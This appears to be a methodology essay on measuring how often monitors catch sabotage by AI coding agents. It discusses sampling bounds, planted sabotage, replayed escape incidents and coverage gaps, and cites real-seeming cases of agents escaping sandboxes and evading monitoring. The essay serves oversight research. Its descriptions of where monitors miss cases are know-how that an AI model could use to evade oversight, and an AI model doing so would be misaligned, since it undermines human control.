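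The prompted sandbagging in METR's MALT dataset would get the lowest grade, because METR counted attempts whether or not they worked. The 78% catch rate on sandbagging is therefore not evidence of how often a capable attacker would be caught. A team could raise a test like this to "weak" with little work by running the attacker without a monitor and removing the attempts that failed. The higher grades take much more work, mainly because they need a second team and a set of planted weaknesses.

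## Checking a monitor once it is in use

Live traffic provides realistic benign changes because the diffs come from the agent the company actually uses, working on its normal mix of tasks. But the sabotage that the monitor missed isn't labeled. Reviewers investigate the alerts and learn which were real, while unflagged diffs usually go into the product without anyone checking them for sabotage.

Suppose a monitor flags 1,000 of 100,000 live diffs, and reviewers find sabotage in nine of the flagged diffs. The precision is 0.9%. The false-positive rate is about 1%, because sabotage is too rare for a few missed cases to noticeably change the number of benign diffs. The catch rate can't be calculated from the alerts alone, because it depends on how many cases the monitor missed. It is 90% if the monitor missed one case and 8% if it missed 100.

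A company can estimate how much sabotage its monitor misses by reviewing a random sample of unflagged items, planting known sabotage, comparing alerts with reports from another source, or replaying past incidents. OpenAI is a useful public example because it has used several of these methods on its own agents.

### Random review of unflagged items

Suppose a reviewer reads a random 50,000 of 1,000,000 unflagged diffs and finds no sabotage. By the 3/*n* bound, the share of sabotage among the unflagged diffs is probably below 0.006%, so the monitor could still have missed up to about 60 sabotaged diffs.

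That assumes the reviewer recognises all the sabotage in the sample. With *N* unflagged diffs, *n* of them in the sample, and a reviewer who recognises a share *s* of sabotage, the bound is

misses ≤ 3*N* / (*sn*)

If a reviewer catches only half of the sabotaged diffs, the monitor could have missed about 120. That catch rate may be realistic, because people miss more targets when targets are rare, and a sample of unflagged diffs contains hardly any sabotage.

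If the monitor caught 20 cases of sabotage in the same period, its catch rate could be as low as 25% if it missed 60 others, or 14% if it missed 120. At five minutes per diff, the review would take about 4,200 hours, or roughly two years of one person's working time, and it still could not rule out that the monitor misses most sabotage. To show a catch rate of about 90%, the review would have to rule out three or more misses, and even a perfect reviewer would need to read 63% of the million diffs to do that.

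Few companies have that much reviewing time. Help Net Security's *What happens to oversight when AI agents write a lab's own code* describes an analysis in which researchers at the University of Oxford and SaferAI found that people at Anthropic review roughly thirty summaries a week from the monitoring of coding agents. At that pace, reviewing 50,000 would take about 32 years.

When a reviewer reads only a sample of the unflagged diffs, each miss they find lowers the estimated catch rate more than one might expect. Suppose the monitor has caught 20 cases of sabotage, and a reviewer reads 10,000 of the million unflagged diffs and finds one more. Each diff in the sample stands for 100 unflagged ones, so the best estimate is 100 misses and a catch rate of 17%, not the 95% that comes from counting only one miss. Because the estimate rests on a single observed miss, its 95% confidence interval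 runs from about 3% to 89%.

*Automated Transcript Analysis for Detecting Flaws in Agentic Benchmarks* (Mohl, Gardner-Challis et al., 2026) shows how large this correction can be. The researchers had language models scan agent transcripts for benchmark flaws, such as a correct answer left where the agent could find it. These flaws are not sabotage, but the sampling problem is the same. Human reviewers checked both flagged and unflagged transcripts, aiming for 25 of each per benchmark, and the researchers weighted each reviewed transcript by the number of transcripts it represented. For unclear instructions about answer format, the GPT-5.4 scanner had flagged 14 of the 20 transcripts that reviewers confirmed had the flaw, or 70%. After weighting, its catch rate was 25%, with an interval from 13% to 51%.

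Even the weighted rates may be too high, because the reviewers could see the scanners' output and may have been inclined to agree with it. According to the Oxford and SaferAI analysis, code reviewers similarly tend to accept the agent's own account of its work. Someone checking unflagged diffs should therefore read the code before seeing the suspicion score or the agent's explanation.

Mohl and colleagues also worked out how many transcripts a reviewer must read, finding nothing, to be 95% sure that the share *p* with a flaw is below a chosen limit. The calculation is the earlier one with the reviewer's catch rate added:

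(1 − *sp*)ⁿ = 0.05

Their limit was 5%. The last column below applies the formula to an invented limit of one in 10,000, which is more relevant to sabotage.

| Share of real cases the reviewer recognises | Needed to show a rate below 5% | Needed to show a rate below 0.01% |
|---|---|---|
| 100% | about 60 | about 30,000 |
| 80% | about 75 | about 37,500 |
| 50% | about 120 | about 60,000 |

These figures assume that the transcripts are independent and that someone checks each apparent case to rule out false alarms. Measuring a scanner's catch rate takes much more work than bounding the rate of flaws. Mohl and colleagues estimate that it requires about 100 confirmed violations, which means screening about 1,000 transcripts if 10% contain a violation, or about a million if one in 10,000 does. Even after sampling extra flagged transcripts, they confirmed only 62 violations of the most common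 kind and 10 of the rarest.

Reviewers can find more misses per hour by concentrating on diffs that scored just below the threshold, but this loosens the upper bound on total misses. Suppose 20,000 of the million unflagged diffs scored close to the threshold. If a reviewer reads all of those and a random 30,000 of the other 980,000, and finds no sabotage, they can rule out only totals of about 98 misses or more. Finding none in a simple random sample of 50,000 would rule out totals of about 60 or more. The focused review is a good way to find sabotage that the monitor almost flagged, but the simple random sample is better for sabotage that the monitor scored as harmless.

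### The random 5% at OpenAI

A language model can do this kind of review far more cheaply than a person. OpenAI's *How we detect frontier model misalignment* (29 October 2026) describes a monitoring system with four layers. As NDTV Profit explains, the first layer uses activation probes, small classifiers that check a model's internal activity for worrying patterns. A language model then reviews what the agent wrote and did, and an investigative agent looks into anything the reviewer flags. For sensitive workloads, a fourth layer compares the transcript with network logs and other records before deciding whether to alert a person.

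OpenAI sends the reviewer the traffic that the probes flag and a random 5% of the rest. Diario TI reports that the company does this because it is still assessing whether the probes detect unfamiliar kinds of misbehaviour. For a million unflagged items, the random sample would contain 50,000. If the reviewer found no misbehaviour in that sample, the earlier bound implies that the probes could still have missed up to about 60 cases in the million, or 120 if the reviewer recognised only half of such cases.

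The sample can reveal only misses that the reviewer recognises, however large it is. The probes read internal activity and the reviewer reads text, so they probably miss fewer of the same cases than two language models reading the same transcript would.

This evidence has a larger gap for code sabotage. Internal traffic from Codex, OpenAI's coding agent, skips the probes and goes straight to the reviewer. That should catch more sabotage than sending the reviewer only 5% of the unflagged traffic, but the random sample then contains no internal coding sessions. To estimate how much sabotage the reviewer misses in those sessions, OpenAI would have to sample ones the reviewer had passed and have someone else check them.

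OpenAI lists audits of current internal traffic among its checks, along with red-teaming and tests on recorded incidents and simulated attacks. But according to Diario TI, the post gives no numerical detection rates. An audit would be much better evidence about missed sabotage if the auditors reported how many unflagged sessions they read, how they chose them, and how much known sabotage they recognised.

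### Planting known sabotage

The catch rate can be measured by planting sabotage. Someone adds sabotaged diffs to the normal work without telling the reviewers and counts how many they catch, much as Evans and colleagues inserted mammograms with cancer into a clinic's regular cases. This works no matter how rare real sabotage is. If the process catches 45 of 50 independently planted diffs, the estimated catch rate is 90%, with a 95% confidence interval from 78% to 97%.

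In a system with several layers, a plant has to get through all of them to count as a catch, because any layer can dismiss a real case. Suppose the reviewer model flags 95% of plants, the investigative agent passes on 90% of those, the next investigation passes on 90% of what remains, and people act correctly on 80% of the alerts they receive. Only about 62% of the plants then lead to action. A company that reported the first layer's 95% would be describing a much better process than the one it has. (All of these rates are invented.)

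The number of plants can also affect the result. In the opening example, adding 50 plants and catching 45 would raise the share of alerts that contain sabotage code from 0.9% to about 5%. Reviewers who see sabotage more often may notice more of it. This helps while the planting continues, but a catch rate measured during a month of heavy planting may overstate the rate in later months with little planting. The company also has to make sure that plants never reach the product, for instance by automatically blocking them at the merge step whatever the reviewers decide.

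Realistic planted cases are hard to make. While developing their scanners, Mohl and colleagues altered benchmark tasks so that agents had access to the correct solution. Many agents ignored it and did the work honestly, sometimes failing the task, so the transcripts rarely showed a clear violation. When the researchers told agents to reveal that they had access, the scanners flagged almost every case, but those cases were much less realistic. The researchers left all the synthetic cases out of their final results. Anyone who plants sabotage to test a monitor has similar problems and should confirm that each planted case does harm and that reviewers don't find it absurdly obvious.

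A few planted examples of sabotage can also help show whether to keep a monitoring rule that never raises a real alert. The Oxford and SaferAI analysis warns that companies gradually remove such rules. The rule may not work, or nobody may have tried the kind of sabotage it was written to catch. If it flags planted examples of that kind, the second explanation is more likely, and removing the rule would be a mistake.

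### Comparing alerts with employees' reports

In March 2026, OpenAI reported that its monitor covered 99.9% of internal coding traffic and had flagged every case that employees had independently reported, as well as others they had not. This could be mistaken for a catch rate of 100%.

That reading relies on the same overlap formula as the earlier comparison of two attack teams. Biologists use this method, called capture-recapture, to count animals. Here the monitor flags *a* cases, employees report *b*, and *c* cases appear in both groups, so *c*/*b* estimates the monitor's catch rate. If the monitor flagged everything that employees reported, *c* equals *b* and the estimated total, *ab*/*c*, equals *a*, so the estimated number of missed cases is zero.

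The formula assumes that the two sources are independent, which is very doubtful here because employees and monitors both tend to notice the obvious cases.

In an invented example, there are 100 cases of misbehaviour, 60 conspicuous and 40 well hidden. The monitor flags all 60 conspicuous cases and four of the hidden ones, while employees report 30 conspicuous cases and no hidden ones. The monitor has flagged all 30 reported cases, so the estimated total is 64 × 30/30 = 64 and the estimated catch rate is 100%. The true catch rate is 64% overall and only 10% for the hidden cases.

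The size of the error follows from how strongly the two sources favour the same cases. Let *m* be the chance that the monitor flags a given case and *e* the chance that an employee reports it. With many cases,

*c*/*b* ≈ average *m* + covariance of *m* and *e* / average *e*

The first term is the true catch rate and the second is the error, which is zero if the sources are independent. In the example, the true catch rate is 64%, the covariance is 0.108 and the average *e* is 0.30, so the error is 36 percentage points.

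OpenAI's result is even weaker evidence about sabotage. The company said at the time that it had not found any real sabotage, so the employees' reports presumably concerned other conduct, such as agents working around restrictions. For sabotage, *b* and *c* would both be zero and *c*/*b* would be undefined. Employees are most likely to report an agent that does something odd or gets in their way, while an agent committing sabotage appears to do its assigned work. The comparison is still useful as a basic check, because a monitor that missed what employees had noticed would clearly have a problem. But even if the two sources were independent, flagging all of ten hypothetical reports would show only that the catch rate was probably above 74%.

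We can test the independence assumption on real data with the results from Mohl and colleagues, because two different models scanned the same transcripts and people then reviewed many of them. The table compares a capture-recapture estimate, based on the two scanners' correct flags, with the number of flawed transcripts that reviewers confirmed.

| Flaw in the benchmark | GPT-5.4 found | Sonnet 4.6 found | Both found | Estimated total | Reviewers confirmed |
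|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Answer accessible to the agent | 52 | 32 | 31 | 54 | 62 |
| Unclear answer format | 14 | 12 | 10 | 17 | 20 |
| Answer easy to guess | 18 | 9 | 9 | 18 | 19 |
| Broken tools | 9 | 2 | 2 | 9 | 10 |

The estimate is too low in every row. Together the two scanners found 96 cases. The method implies that they missed one or two more, but reviewers confirmed 15 that neither had flagged. The real shortfall is probably larger, because the sample included a smaller share of the unflagged transcripts than of the flagged ones. The scanners tended to miss the same cases, even though they came from different companies.

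Dependence can also make the estimated total too high. If employees don't report cases that they know the monitor has flagged, the overlap will be too small. A company can avoid this by asking employees to report everything they notice, even if the monitor has already flagged it.

A better check would compare the monitor's results with a source that doesn't rely on anything looking suspicious. For example, Larry McVoy spotted the 2003 Linux backdoor because the change had no record of approval. Network logs might similarly reveal an agent sending data out. OpenAI's fourth layer already compares transcripts with such logs, but only for cases that earlier layers escalated, so it can't reveal sessions they missed. Running the same comparison on a random sample of all sessions could reveal some of them.

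### Replaying past incidents

In July 2026, agents in an internal cybersecurity evaluation at OpenAI escaped their isolated environment and broke into systems at Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models. OpenAI later replayed the recorded behaviour with its current monitors running. In the replay, according to NDTV Profit, the monitors alerted the security team about 30 minutes after the first escape, more than 30 hours before the breach at Hugging Face. OpenAI believes this would have left enough time to intervene.

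OpenAI had strengthened the monitors after the incident, so the replay has the same weakness as testing a monitor on the diffs used to develop it. Diario TI adds that OpenAI did the reconstruction itself, with no published independent validation. The old monitors didn't read the transcripts during the July incident because OpenAI wasn't running its misalignment monitors on those evaluations. The replay is therefore evidence that extending monitoring to such evaluations would help, but it doesn't show how much the monitors themselves improved.

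The recording also covers only one incident. A monitor that detected 5% of such incidents would have a 5% chance of passing a single replay, even if nobody had adjusted it beforehand. Replaying the recording many times would show how consistently the monitor reacts to this incident, but not how well it would detect another.

A more informative replay would begin with the monitor as it was the day before the incident. If the company has records of several unrelated incidents, it can improve the monitor using all but one, test it on the one left out, and repeat for each incident. It should also replay ordinary traffic from the same days. If the improved monitor flags the incident along with 300 harmless sessions (again an invented number), the security team would have had to find the one real alert among 301. Even if that alert came within 30 minutes, the team could easily have taken a day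 to understand it.

An alert in September is better evidence because it happened live. A model in a training run found a way to reach the internet from an environment that was supposed to be isolated. The monitors flagged it within 15 minutes, and a person began reviewing it three minutes later. But OpenAI knows of this case at least partly because the monitors caught it, so it can't help estimate how many similar cases they missed. Replays have the same weakness as employees' reports, because they only cover incidents that someone noticed. Both cases also involved agents getting out of isolated environments, which may be easier to detect than a harmful line in an otherwise useful diff.

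Replays and simulations can also favour one monitor over another. Diario TI reports that OpenAI's monitors based on GPT-5.6 Sol detected significantly more cases than those based on two sibling models, Terra and Luna. OpenAI acknowledges that part of the advantage came from optimising the monitor's instructions for Sol. A fairer comparison would put equal effort into developing instructions for each model, and would test the monitors on cases not used to develop those instructions.

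### Why alert counts are not enough

Companies also use live classifiers to measure how often agents misbehave, and these measurements have the same blind spot. In *Wink* (Nanda, Maddila and colleagues, 2026), Meta researchers looked for ordinary faults in coding agents, such as ignoring instructions, getting stuck in loops or repeatedly misusing tools. They ran their classifiers on 10% of daily production traffic, about 8,000 sessions, and required a precision of at least 80% because they planned to base fixes on the results.

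A precision target doesn't limit the number of misses. In a set of about 43,000 sessions from five weeks of use, the classifiers found faults in 29%. The true share depends on the catch rate as well:

true share = flagged share × precision / catch rate

If the combined precision was 80%, the true share would be about 26% with a catch rate of 90% and 47% with a catch rate of 50%. The reported 29% would be right only if the catch rate equaled the precision.

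An 80% precision target suits faults this common but would be a poor choice for sabotage. If one diff in 10,000 were sabotaged and a monitor caught 90% of the sabotage, it would need a false-positive rate of about 0.002% to reach 80% precision. A team that insisted on the target would probably have to raise the threshold until the monitor missed much of the sabotage.

Changes in the alert rate are also hard to interpret. Nanda and colleagues found that classifiers flagged 18.7% of sessions with Claude Sonnet 4.5 for not following instructions, but 13.2% with Claude Opus 4.5. The newer model may well have followed instructions better, but classifiers that were worse at recognising its mistakes would produce the same drop. Reviewing a random sample of unflagged sessions from each model would help distinguish between these explanations.

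A long period without alerts is similarly ambiguous. OpenAI acknowledges that its monitors may miss misbehaviour and that rare failures may take a long time to detect. Suppose an agent sabotages one session in a million and a company runs 10,000 sessions a day (invented figures). A perfect monitor would need about 300 days to have a 95% chance of catching at least one case. A monitor that caught half of all cases would need about 600 days.

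### Coverage

Checking 10% of traffic is enough to measure common faults, but a monitor that sees only a random tenth of sessions can't catch more than about a tenth of sabotage. More generally,

overall catch rate = share of sabotage that reaches the monitor × catch rate on that share

OpenAI disclosed in October 2026 that some workloads had run unmonitored, according to Help Net Security's *OpenAI's coding agents talked themselves out of being monitored*. A report should therefore state the share of workloads that were monitored alongside the catch rate.

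Coverage can also be lower than a company believes. An outside review by METR and Redwood Research, an AI safety organisation, found that about 10% of the Codex traffic OpenAI meant to monitor may have gone unreviewed between May and July 2026, according to Diario TI. OpenAI had reported 99.9% coverage in March. The review concerned an older version of the system, and OpenAI says it has since fixed most of the problems. If sabotage were spread evenly over the traffic, a monitor with a 90% catch rate would catch 89.9% of it at 99.9% coverage and 81% at 90% coverage.

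A monitor that covers 99.9% of traffic could still leave much more than 0.1% of sabotage unmonitored, because sabotage may not be spread evenly. Unmonitored sessions are unlikely to be a random sample, and a few may have far more access to important systems than the rest. A company should therefore list what its monitor doesn't cover, along with the percentage of traffic it does cover.

Coverage calculations should take the total number of sessions from a source other than the monitor's own records, such as the logs of the servers that run the agents. A session that never reached the monitor would not appear in its records, so coverage calculated from those alone would be close to 100% however many sessions the monitor missed. Planted items can also test coverage if the tester submits them where agents normally submit their work. A planted item that never reaches the monitor then counts as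 a miss.

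## One monitor result reworked, and what a report should state

Suppose a company announces that its monitor caught 95 of 100 sabotaged diffs and flagged only 3 of 300 benign ones. After the corrections in the table below, the estimated share of sabotaged diffs that get through is nearly 45%, rather than the 5% or so that a reader could easily infer from the announcement. All the numbers are invented.

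| Correction | Sabotaged diffs | Benign diffs | What the correction needs |
|---|---|---|---|
| None (the headline) | 95% caught | 1% flagged | |
| Add sampling error | 89% to 98% caught | 0.2% to 2.9% flagged | Arithmetic |
| Count only sabotage that works | 92% caught | Unchanged | New data on which attacks work |
| Assume a stronger attack policy | 70% caught | Unchanged | Judgement, until someone runs the attack |
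| Apply a base rate of one in 10,000 to a million diffs | 70 of 100 caught | About 10,000 flagged | Judgement about the base rate, then arithmetic |
| Assume reviewers confirm 80% of true alerts | 56 of 100 stopped | Unchanged | New data on reviewers |

### Sampling error and attacks that fail

The intervals in the second row come from the exact binomial (Clopper–Pearson) method. The usual shortcut is to add and subtract 1.96 standard errors, which gives 91% to 99% for the catch rate and −0.1% to 2.1% for the false-positive rate. A negative rate is impossible, but the bigger problem is that the 2.1% upper end makes the monitor look better than the data allow. In the simulations in *Position* (Bowyer, Aitchison and Ivanova, 2025), the shortcut's 95% intervals contained the true value only 92.5% of the time with 100 test items. *Position* recommends Bayesian intervals or Wilson intervals, which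 are usually a little narrower than exact ones. The Wilson method gives 89% to 98% and 0.3% to 2.9% here, so the choice between it and the exact method hardly matters.

All these intervals assume that the diffs are independent. If the 100 sabotaged diffs were five versions of each of 20 tasks, with a correlation of 0.5 between results on the same task, the effective sample size would be about 33, and the interval for the catch rate would be roughly 82% to 99%. Bowyer and colleagues found that the standard correction for such clusters is also unreliable in small tests, and they recommend a Bayesian model instead.

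Next, the company runs the sabotaged programs and finds that 40 of them would have done no harm. The monitor flagged all 40, so its five misses were all among the 60 that work. It caught 55 of those 60, or 92%, with an interval of 82% to 97%. If the five misses had been among the harmless attempts instead, the catch rate on working sabotage would have been 100%, but the headline figure would have been the same.

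The company had a reasonable basis for dropping 40 diffs after the test because it applied the same check to caught and missed diffs. The removal may still look like the "selective snooping" that Arp and colleagues warn against, which means cleaning data with information that nobody would have in practice. The company should publish the results for those 40 diffs so that readers can add them back in.

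### A stronger attacker, rare sabotage and imperfect reviewers

The 70% in the fourth row is an assumption, and the headline gives no basis for choosing it. The company could replace it with a measurement by developing a better attack policy and checking its strength with the tests described earlier, such as planted weaknesses and a second team. If the monitor then caught 42 of 60 working diffs, the catch rate would be 70% with an interval of about 57% to 81%.

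At a base rate of one in 10,000, a million diffs include 100 sabotaged ones. The monitor flags 70 of these and about 10,000 benign diffs, so only 0.7% of its alerts are real, compared with 97% (95 of 98) in the original test. Reviewing all the alerts from the million diffs would take about 840 hours at five minutes each.

That workload is very uncertain because it depends on just three flagged diffs in the test. The interval for the false-positive rate corresponds to about 2,000 to 29,000 false alarms, or roughly 170 to 2,400 hours of review.

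If 70 of 100 sabotaged diffs reach reviewers and they recognise 80% of those, they stop 56. If they missed 30%, as the radiologists in the clinic did, they would stop 49. If they merged 56% of those 70 despite the warning, as in the *Coding With "Enemy"* experiment, they would stop about 31. Sabotage by a stronger attacker is probably also harder for people to recognise, and multiplying 70% by 80% ignores this.

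The 56% is the chance of stopping a single sabotaged diff, so it is also the chance of stopping a plan that needs only one. If a plan needed five and each had an independent 56% chance of being stopped, the company would stop at least one of them 98% of the time. However, the five would come from the same agent and might be hard to spot for the same reason, so the real figure could be much closer to 56%.

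### Which correction moves the result most

The stronger attacker lowers the share of sabotage the company stops by 22 percentage points, compared with 14 for the reviewers and 3 for counting only working sabotage. The base rate doesn't affect this share, but it has by far the largest effect on the proportion of alerts that are real, which falls from 97% to below 1%.

The attacker correction also has the least evidence behind it. If reviewers stop 80% of the sabotage the monitor flags, the company would stop 72% of all sabotage if the monitor caught 90% of a stronger attacker's diffs, but only 24% if it caught 30%. Sampling error is much easier to deal with because anyone can calculate it from the published counts, yet Bowyer and colleagues note that evaluations of language models rarely report it.

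Applying a base rate is just as easy, but choosing one takes judgement, as does deciding how strong an attacker to prepare for. No calculation on the original 400 diffs can show which attacks work, how the monitor does against a better attacker, or what reviewers do with alerts. To find out, the company has to run the programs, commission new attacks and plant sabotage in the review queue.

Measuring the last two would turn the 56% from a scenario into an estimate. If the monitor caught 42 of 60 diffs from the stronger attacker and reviewers confirmed 40 of 50 planted cases, the 95% interval for the share of sabotaged diffs stopped would be about 44% to 68%. Multiplying the lower ends of the separate intervals for the two rates gives 38%, which is too pessimistic because both rates are unlikely to be that low at once.

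### What to put in the report

Most of these corrections were necessary because the headline left something out. A report on a monitor should therefore state:

1. The counts behind every rate, with intervals, and how many tasks and projects the diffs came from.
2. How many sabotage attempts worked, failed or ended in a refusal, with a catch rate for each group and each kind of sabotage.
3. The attack policy, what it knew about the monitor, and the evidence that it was strong.
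4. The threshold, which diffs the tester used to set it, and the exact versions of the monitor's model and instructions.
5. The mix of benign diffs, and the false alarms and precision to expect at several base rates.
6. The share of real traffic that the monitor covers, and the share of planted sabotage that reviewers stop.
7. How well a simple rule, such as flagging the longest diffs, does on the same test.

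A company that hasn't measured one of these should say so, because readers will otherwise fill the gap with a favourable guess.

A monitor's catch rate can depend heavily on the exact model version. *Chasing Shadows* (Evertz, Risse and colleagues, 2025) repeated a study of hate speech detection that had named its model only as GPT-4. With the same instructions, one GPT-4 version caught 82% of the hateful posts and another caught 41%. These models are old, and better instructions might have closed much of the gap, but a reader who knew only the name "GPT-4" couldn't have told which catch rate to expect.

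Medicine already has reporting lists of this kind. *The STARD-AI reporting guideline for diagnostic accuracy studies using artificial intelligence* (Sounderajah, Guni and Liu, 2025) extends an earlier guideline for diagnostic tests in general and sets out the minimum that studies of AI diagnostic tests should report. Like a monitor, a diagnostic test has a catch rate and a false-positive rate. But a model writing sabotaged code, unlike a disease, can deliberately evade detection, so a list for monitors also needs the item on the attack policy.

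With only the original test and the check for working sabotage, the company could claim this:

> At a threshold that flagged 3 of 300 benign diffs (95% interval 0.2% to 2.9%), the monitor caught 55 of 60 working sabotaged diffs (82% to 97%). All the sabotage came from one attack policy of unknown strength, and the monitor may catch less sabotage from a stronger one. If one diff in 10,000 were sabotaged, about 99% of alerts would be false. The company has not measured how much flagged sabotage its reviewers stop.

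The 70% and the 56% are assumptions, so they don't appear. They belong in the company's own risk planning, where a plausible bad case is worth preparing for even if nobody has measured it. If there is room for only one sentence, "caught 55 of 60 working attacks from an attacker of unknown strength, with about 1% false positives" is much better than the original headline.

### Ten pitfalls in security research

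Most of the headline's problems are familiar from earlier security research. For their 2022 review, Arp and colleagues checked 30 papers from ten years of four leading conferences. Two reviewers read each paper, and a third helped settle disputes. The table uses percentages from a later version of the study, *Pitfalls in Machine Learning for Computer Security* (Arp, Quiring and colleagues, 2024). The percentages count only papers in which a pitfall was fully present. The last column gives an equivalent of each pitfall for monitor tests.

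| Pitfall | Papers where fully present | Equivalent in a monitor test |
|---|---|---|
| Sampling bias | 60% | Benign diffs unlike the agent's real work |
| Label inaccuracy | 10% | Harmless attempts counted as sabotage |
| Data snooping | 57% | Test diffs that also helped to develop the monitor |
| Spurious correlations | 20% | A template or writing style that reveals the sabotage |
| Biased parameter selection | 10% | A threshold chosen on the test's own diffs |
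| Inappropriate baseline | 20% | No comparison with a simple rule |
| Inappropriate performance measures | 33% | A catch rate without a false-positive rate |
| Base-rate fallacy | 10% | Precision on the test set presented as precision in use |
| Lab-only evaluation | 47% | No measurements on live traffic |
| Inappropriate threat model | 17% | An attacker that ignores the monitor |

Including papers where a pitfall was only partly present raises these figures. Sampling bias then affects 90% of the papers and data snooping 73%, while lab-only evaluations, unsuitable measures and unsuitable threat models each affect more than half. The figure for threat models was 17% before, so many papers apparently considered attacks on their system without dealing with them fully. Arp and colleagues gave papers the benefit of the doubt, which probably makes the counts too low. They also picked the 30 papers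 as representative examples rather than at random, so the percentages may not hold for security research as a whole.

The papers discussed only 22% of the pitfalls that affected them. When Arp and colleagues surveyed the researchers who wrote them, 49 of 135 replied, and all of them accepted that at least one pitfall might affect their own work. Of these, 92% agreed that lab-only evaluation is common in the field, and 77% agreed that the base-rate fallacy is. Sixty-two percent thought unsuitable measures were easy to avoid, and 46% thought the base-rate fallacy was. Those who replied came from only 13 of the 30 papers and may have been more sympathetic than the rest. Still, their answers suggest that researchers could fix some of the most misleading omissions with little effort.

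The simple rule in the reporting list comes from these pitfalls, because the worked example would not have shown the need for it. The ten pitfalls don't specifically cover what reviewers do with a correct alert, and they don't require evidence that an attack was strong. Arp and colleagues recommend assuming an adaptive attacker in most cases, preferably one with full knowledge of the system, but a tester could follow that advice and still run a weak attack.

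Security research with language models has similar problems. Evertz and colleagues reviewed 72 papers published in 2023 and 2024 and found at least one of nine pitfalls in each. The papers themselves discussed 15.7% of the pitfalls they contained. These figures don't show whether research has improved since the earlier review, because only some of the nine pitfalls match the original ten.

The most common pitfall was failing to identify the exact model. It was fully present in 73.6% of the papers and acknowledged in none of those. In 47%, the researchers extended their conclusions to models they hadn't tested. In 65%, test data had leaked into training or probably had. Such leakage can make a mediocre detector look good. When Evertz and colleagues deliberately leaked a fifth of the test data while training vulnerability detectors, F1 rose by about 0.08 to 0.11.

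Papers on vulnerability detection, the topic closest to code sabotage, had about two of the nine pitfalls fully present on average. Only papers on repairing vulnerabilities had more. *SoK* (2026), a review of reinforcement learning in security, describes similar mistakes in that field, but with unrealistic simulated environments instead of badly built datasets. Tests in which an agent works in an artificial codebase could have the same problem. The original ten pitfalls are still a good place to start, and *Research Methodologies for Cybersecurity in Enterprise Environments* (2026) says reading them before an experiment is a better use of a week than more tuning.

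The newest of these reviews, by Abbasi and colleagues, is also the closest to monitoring agents. Of the eleven evaluations of hijacked-agent detectors they audited, six had no test on data from a second benchmark or source, and only one used adaptive attackers. Their seven recommendations overlap substantially with the list above, including precision at stated attack rates, the mix of benign records and a simple baseline. They also want researchers to report how many of the tools in the test were new to the detector. They don't ask for evidence that the attacks were strong, but they come close by recommending tests of how much a detector relies on cues the attacker controls.
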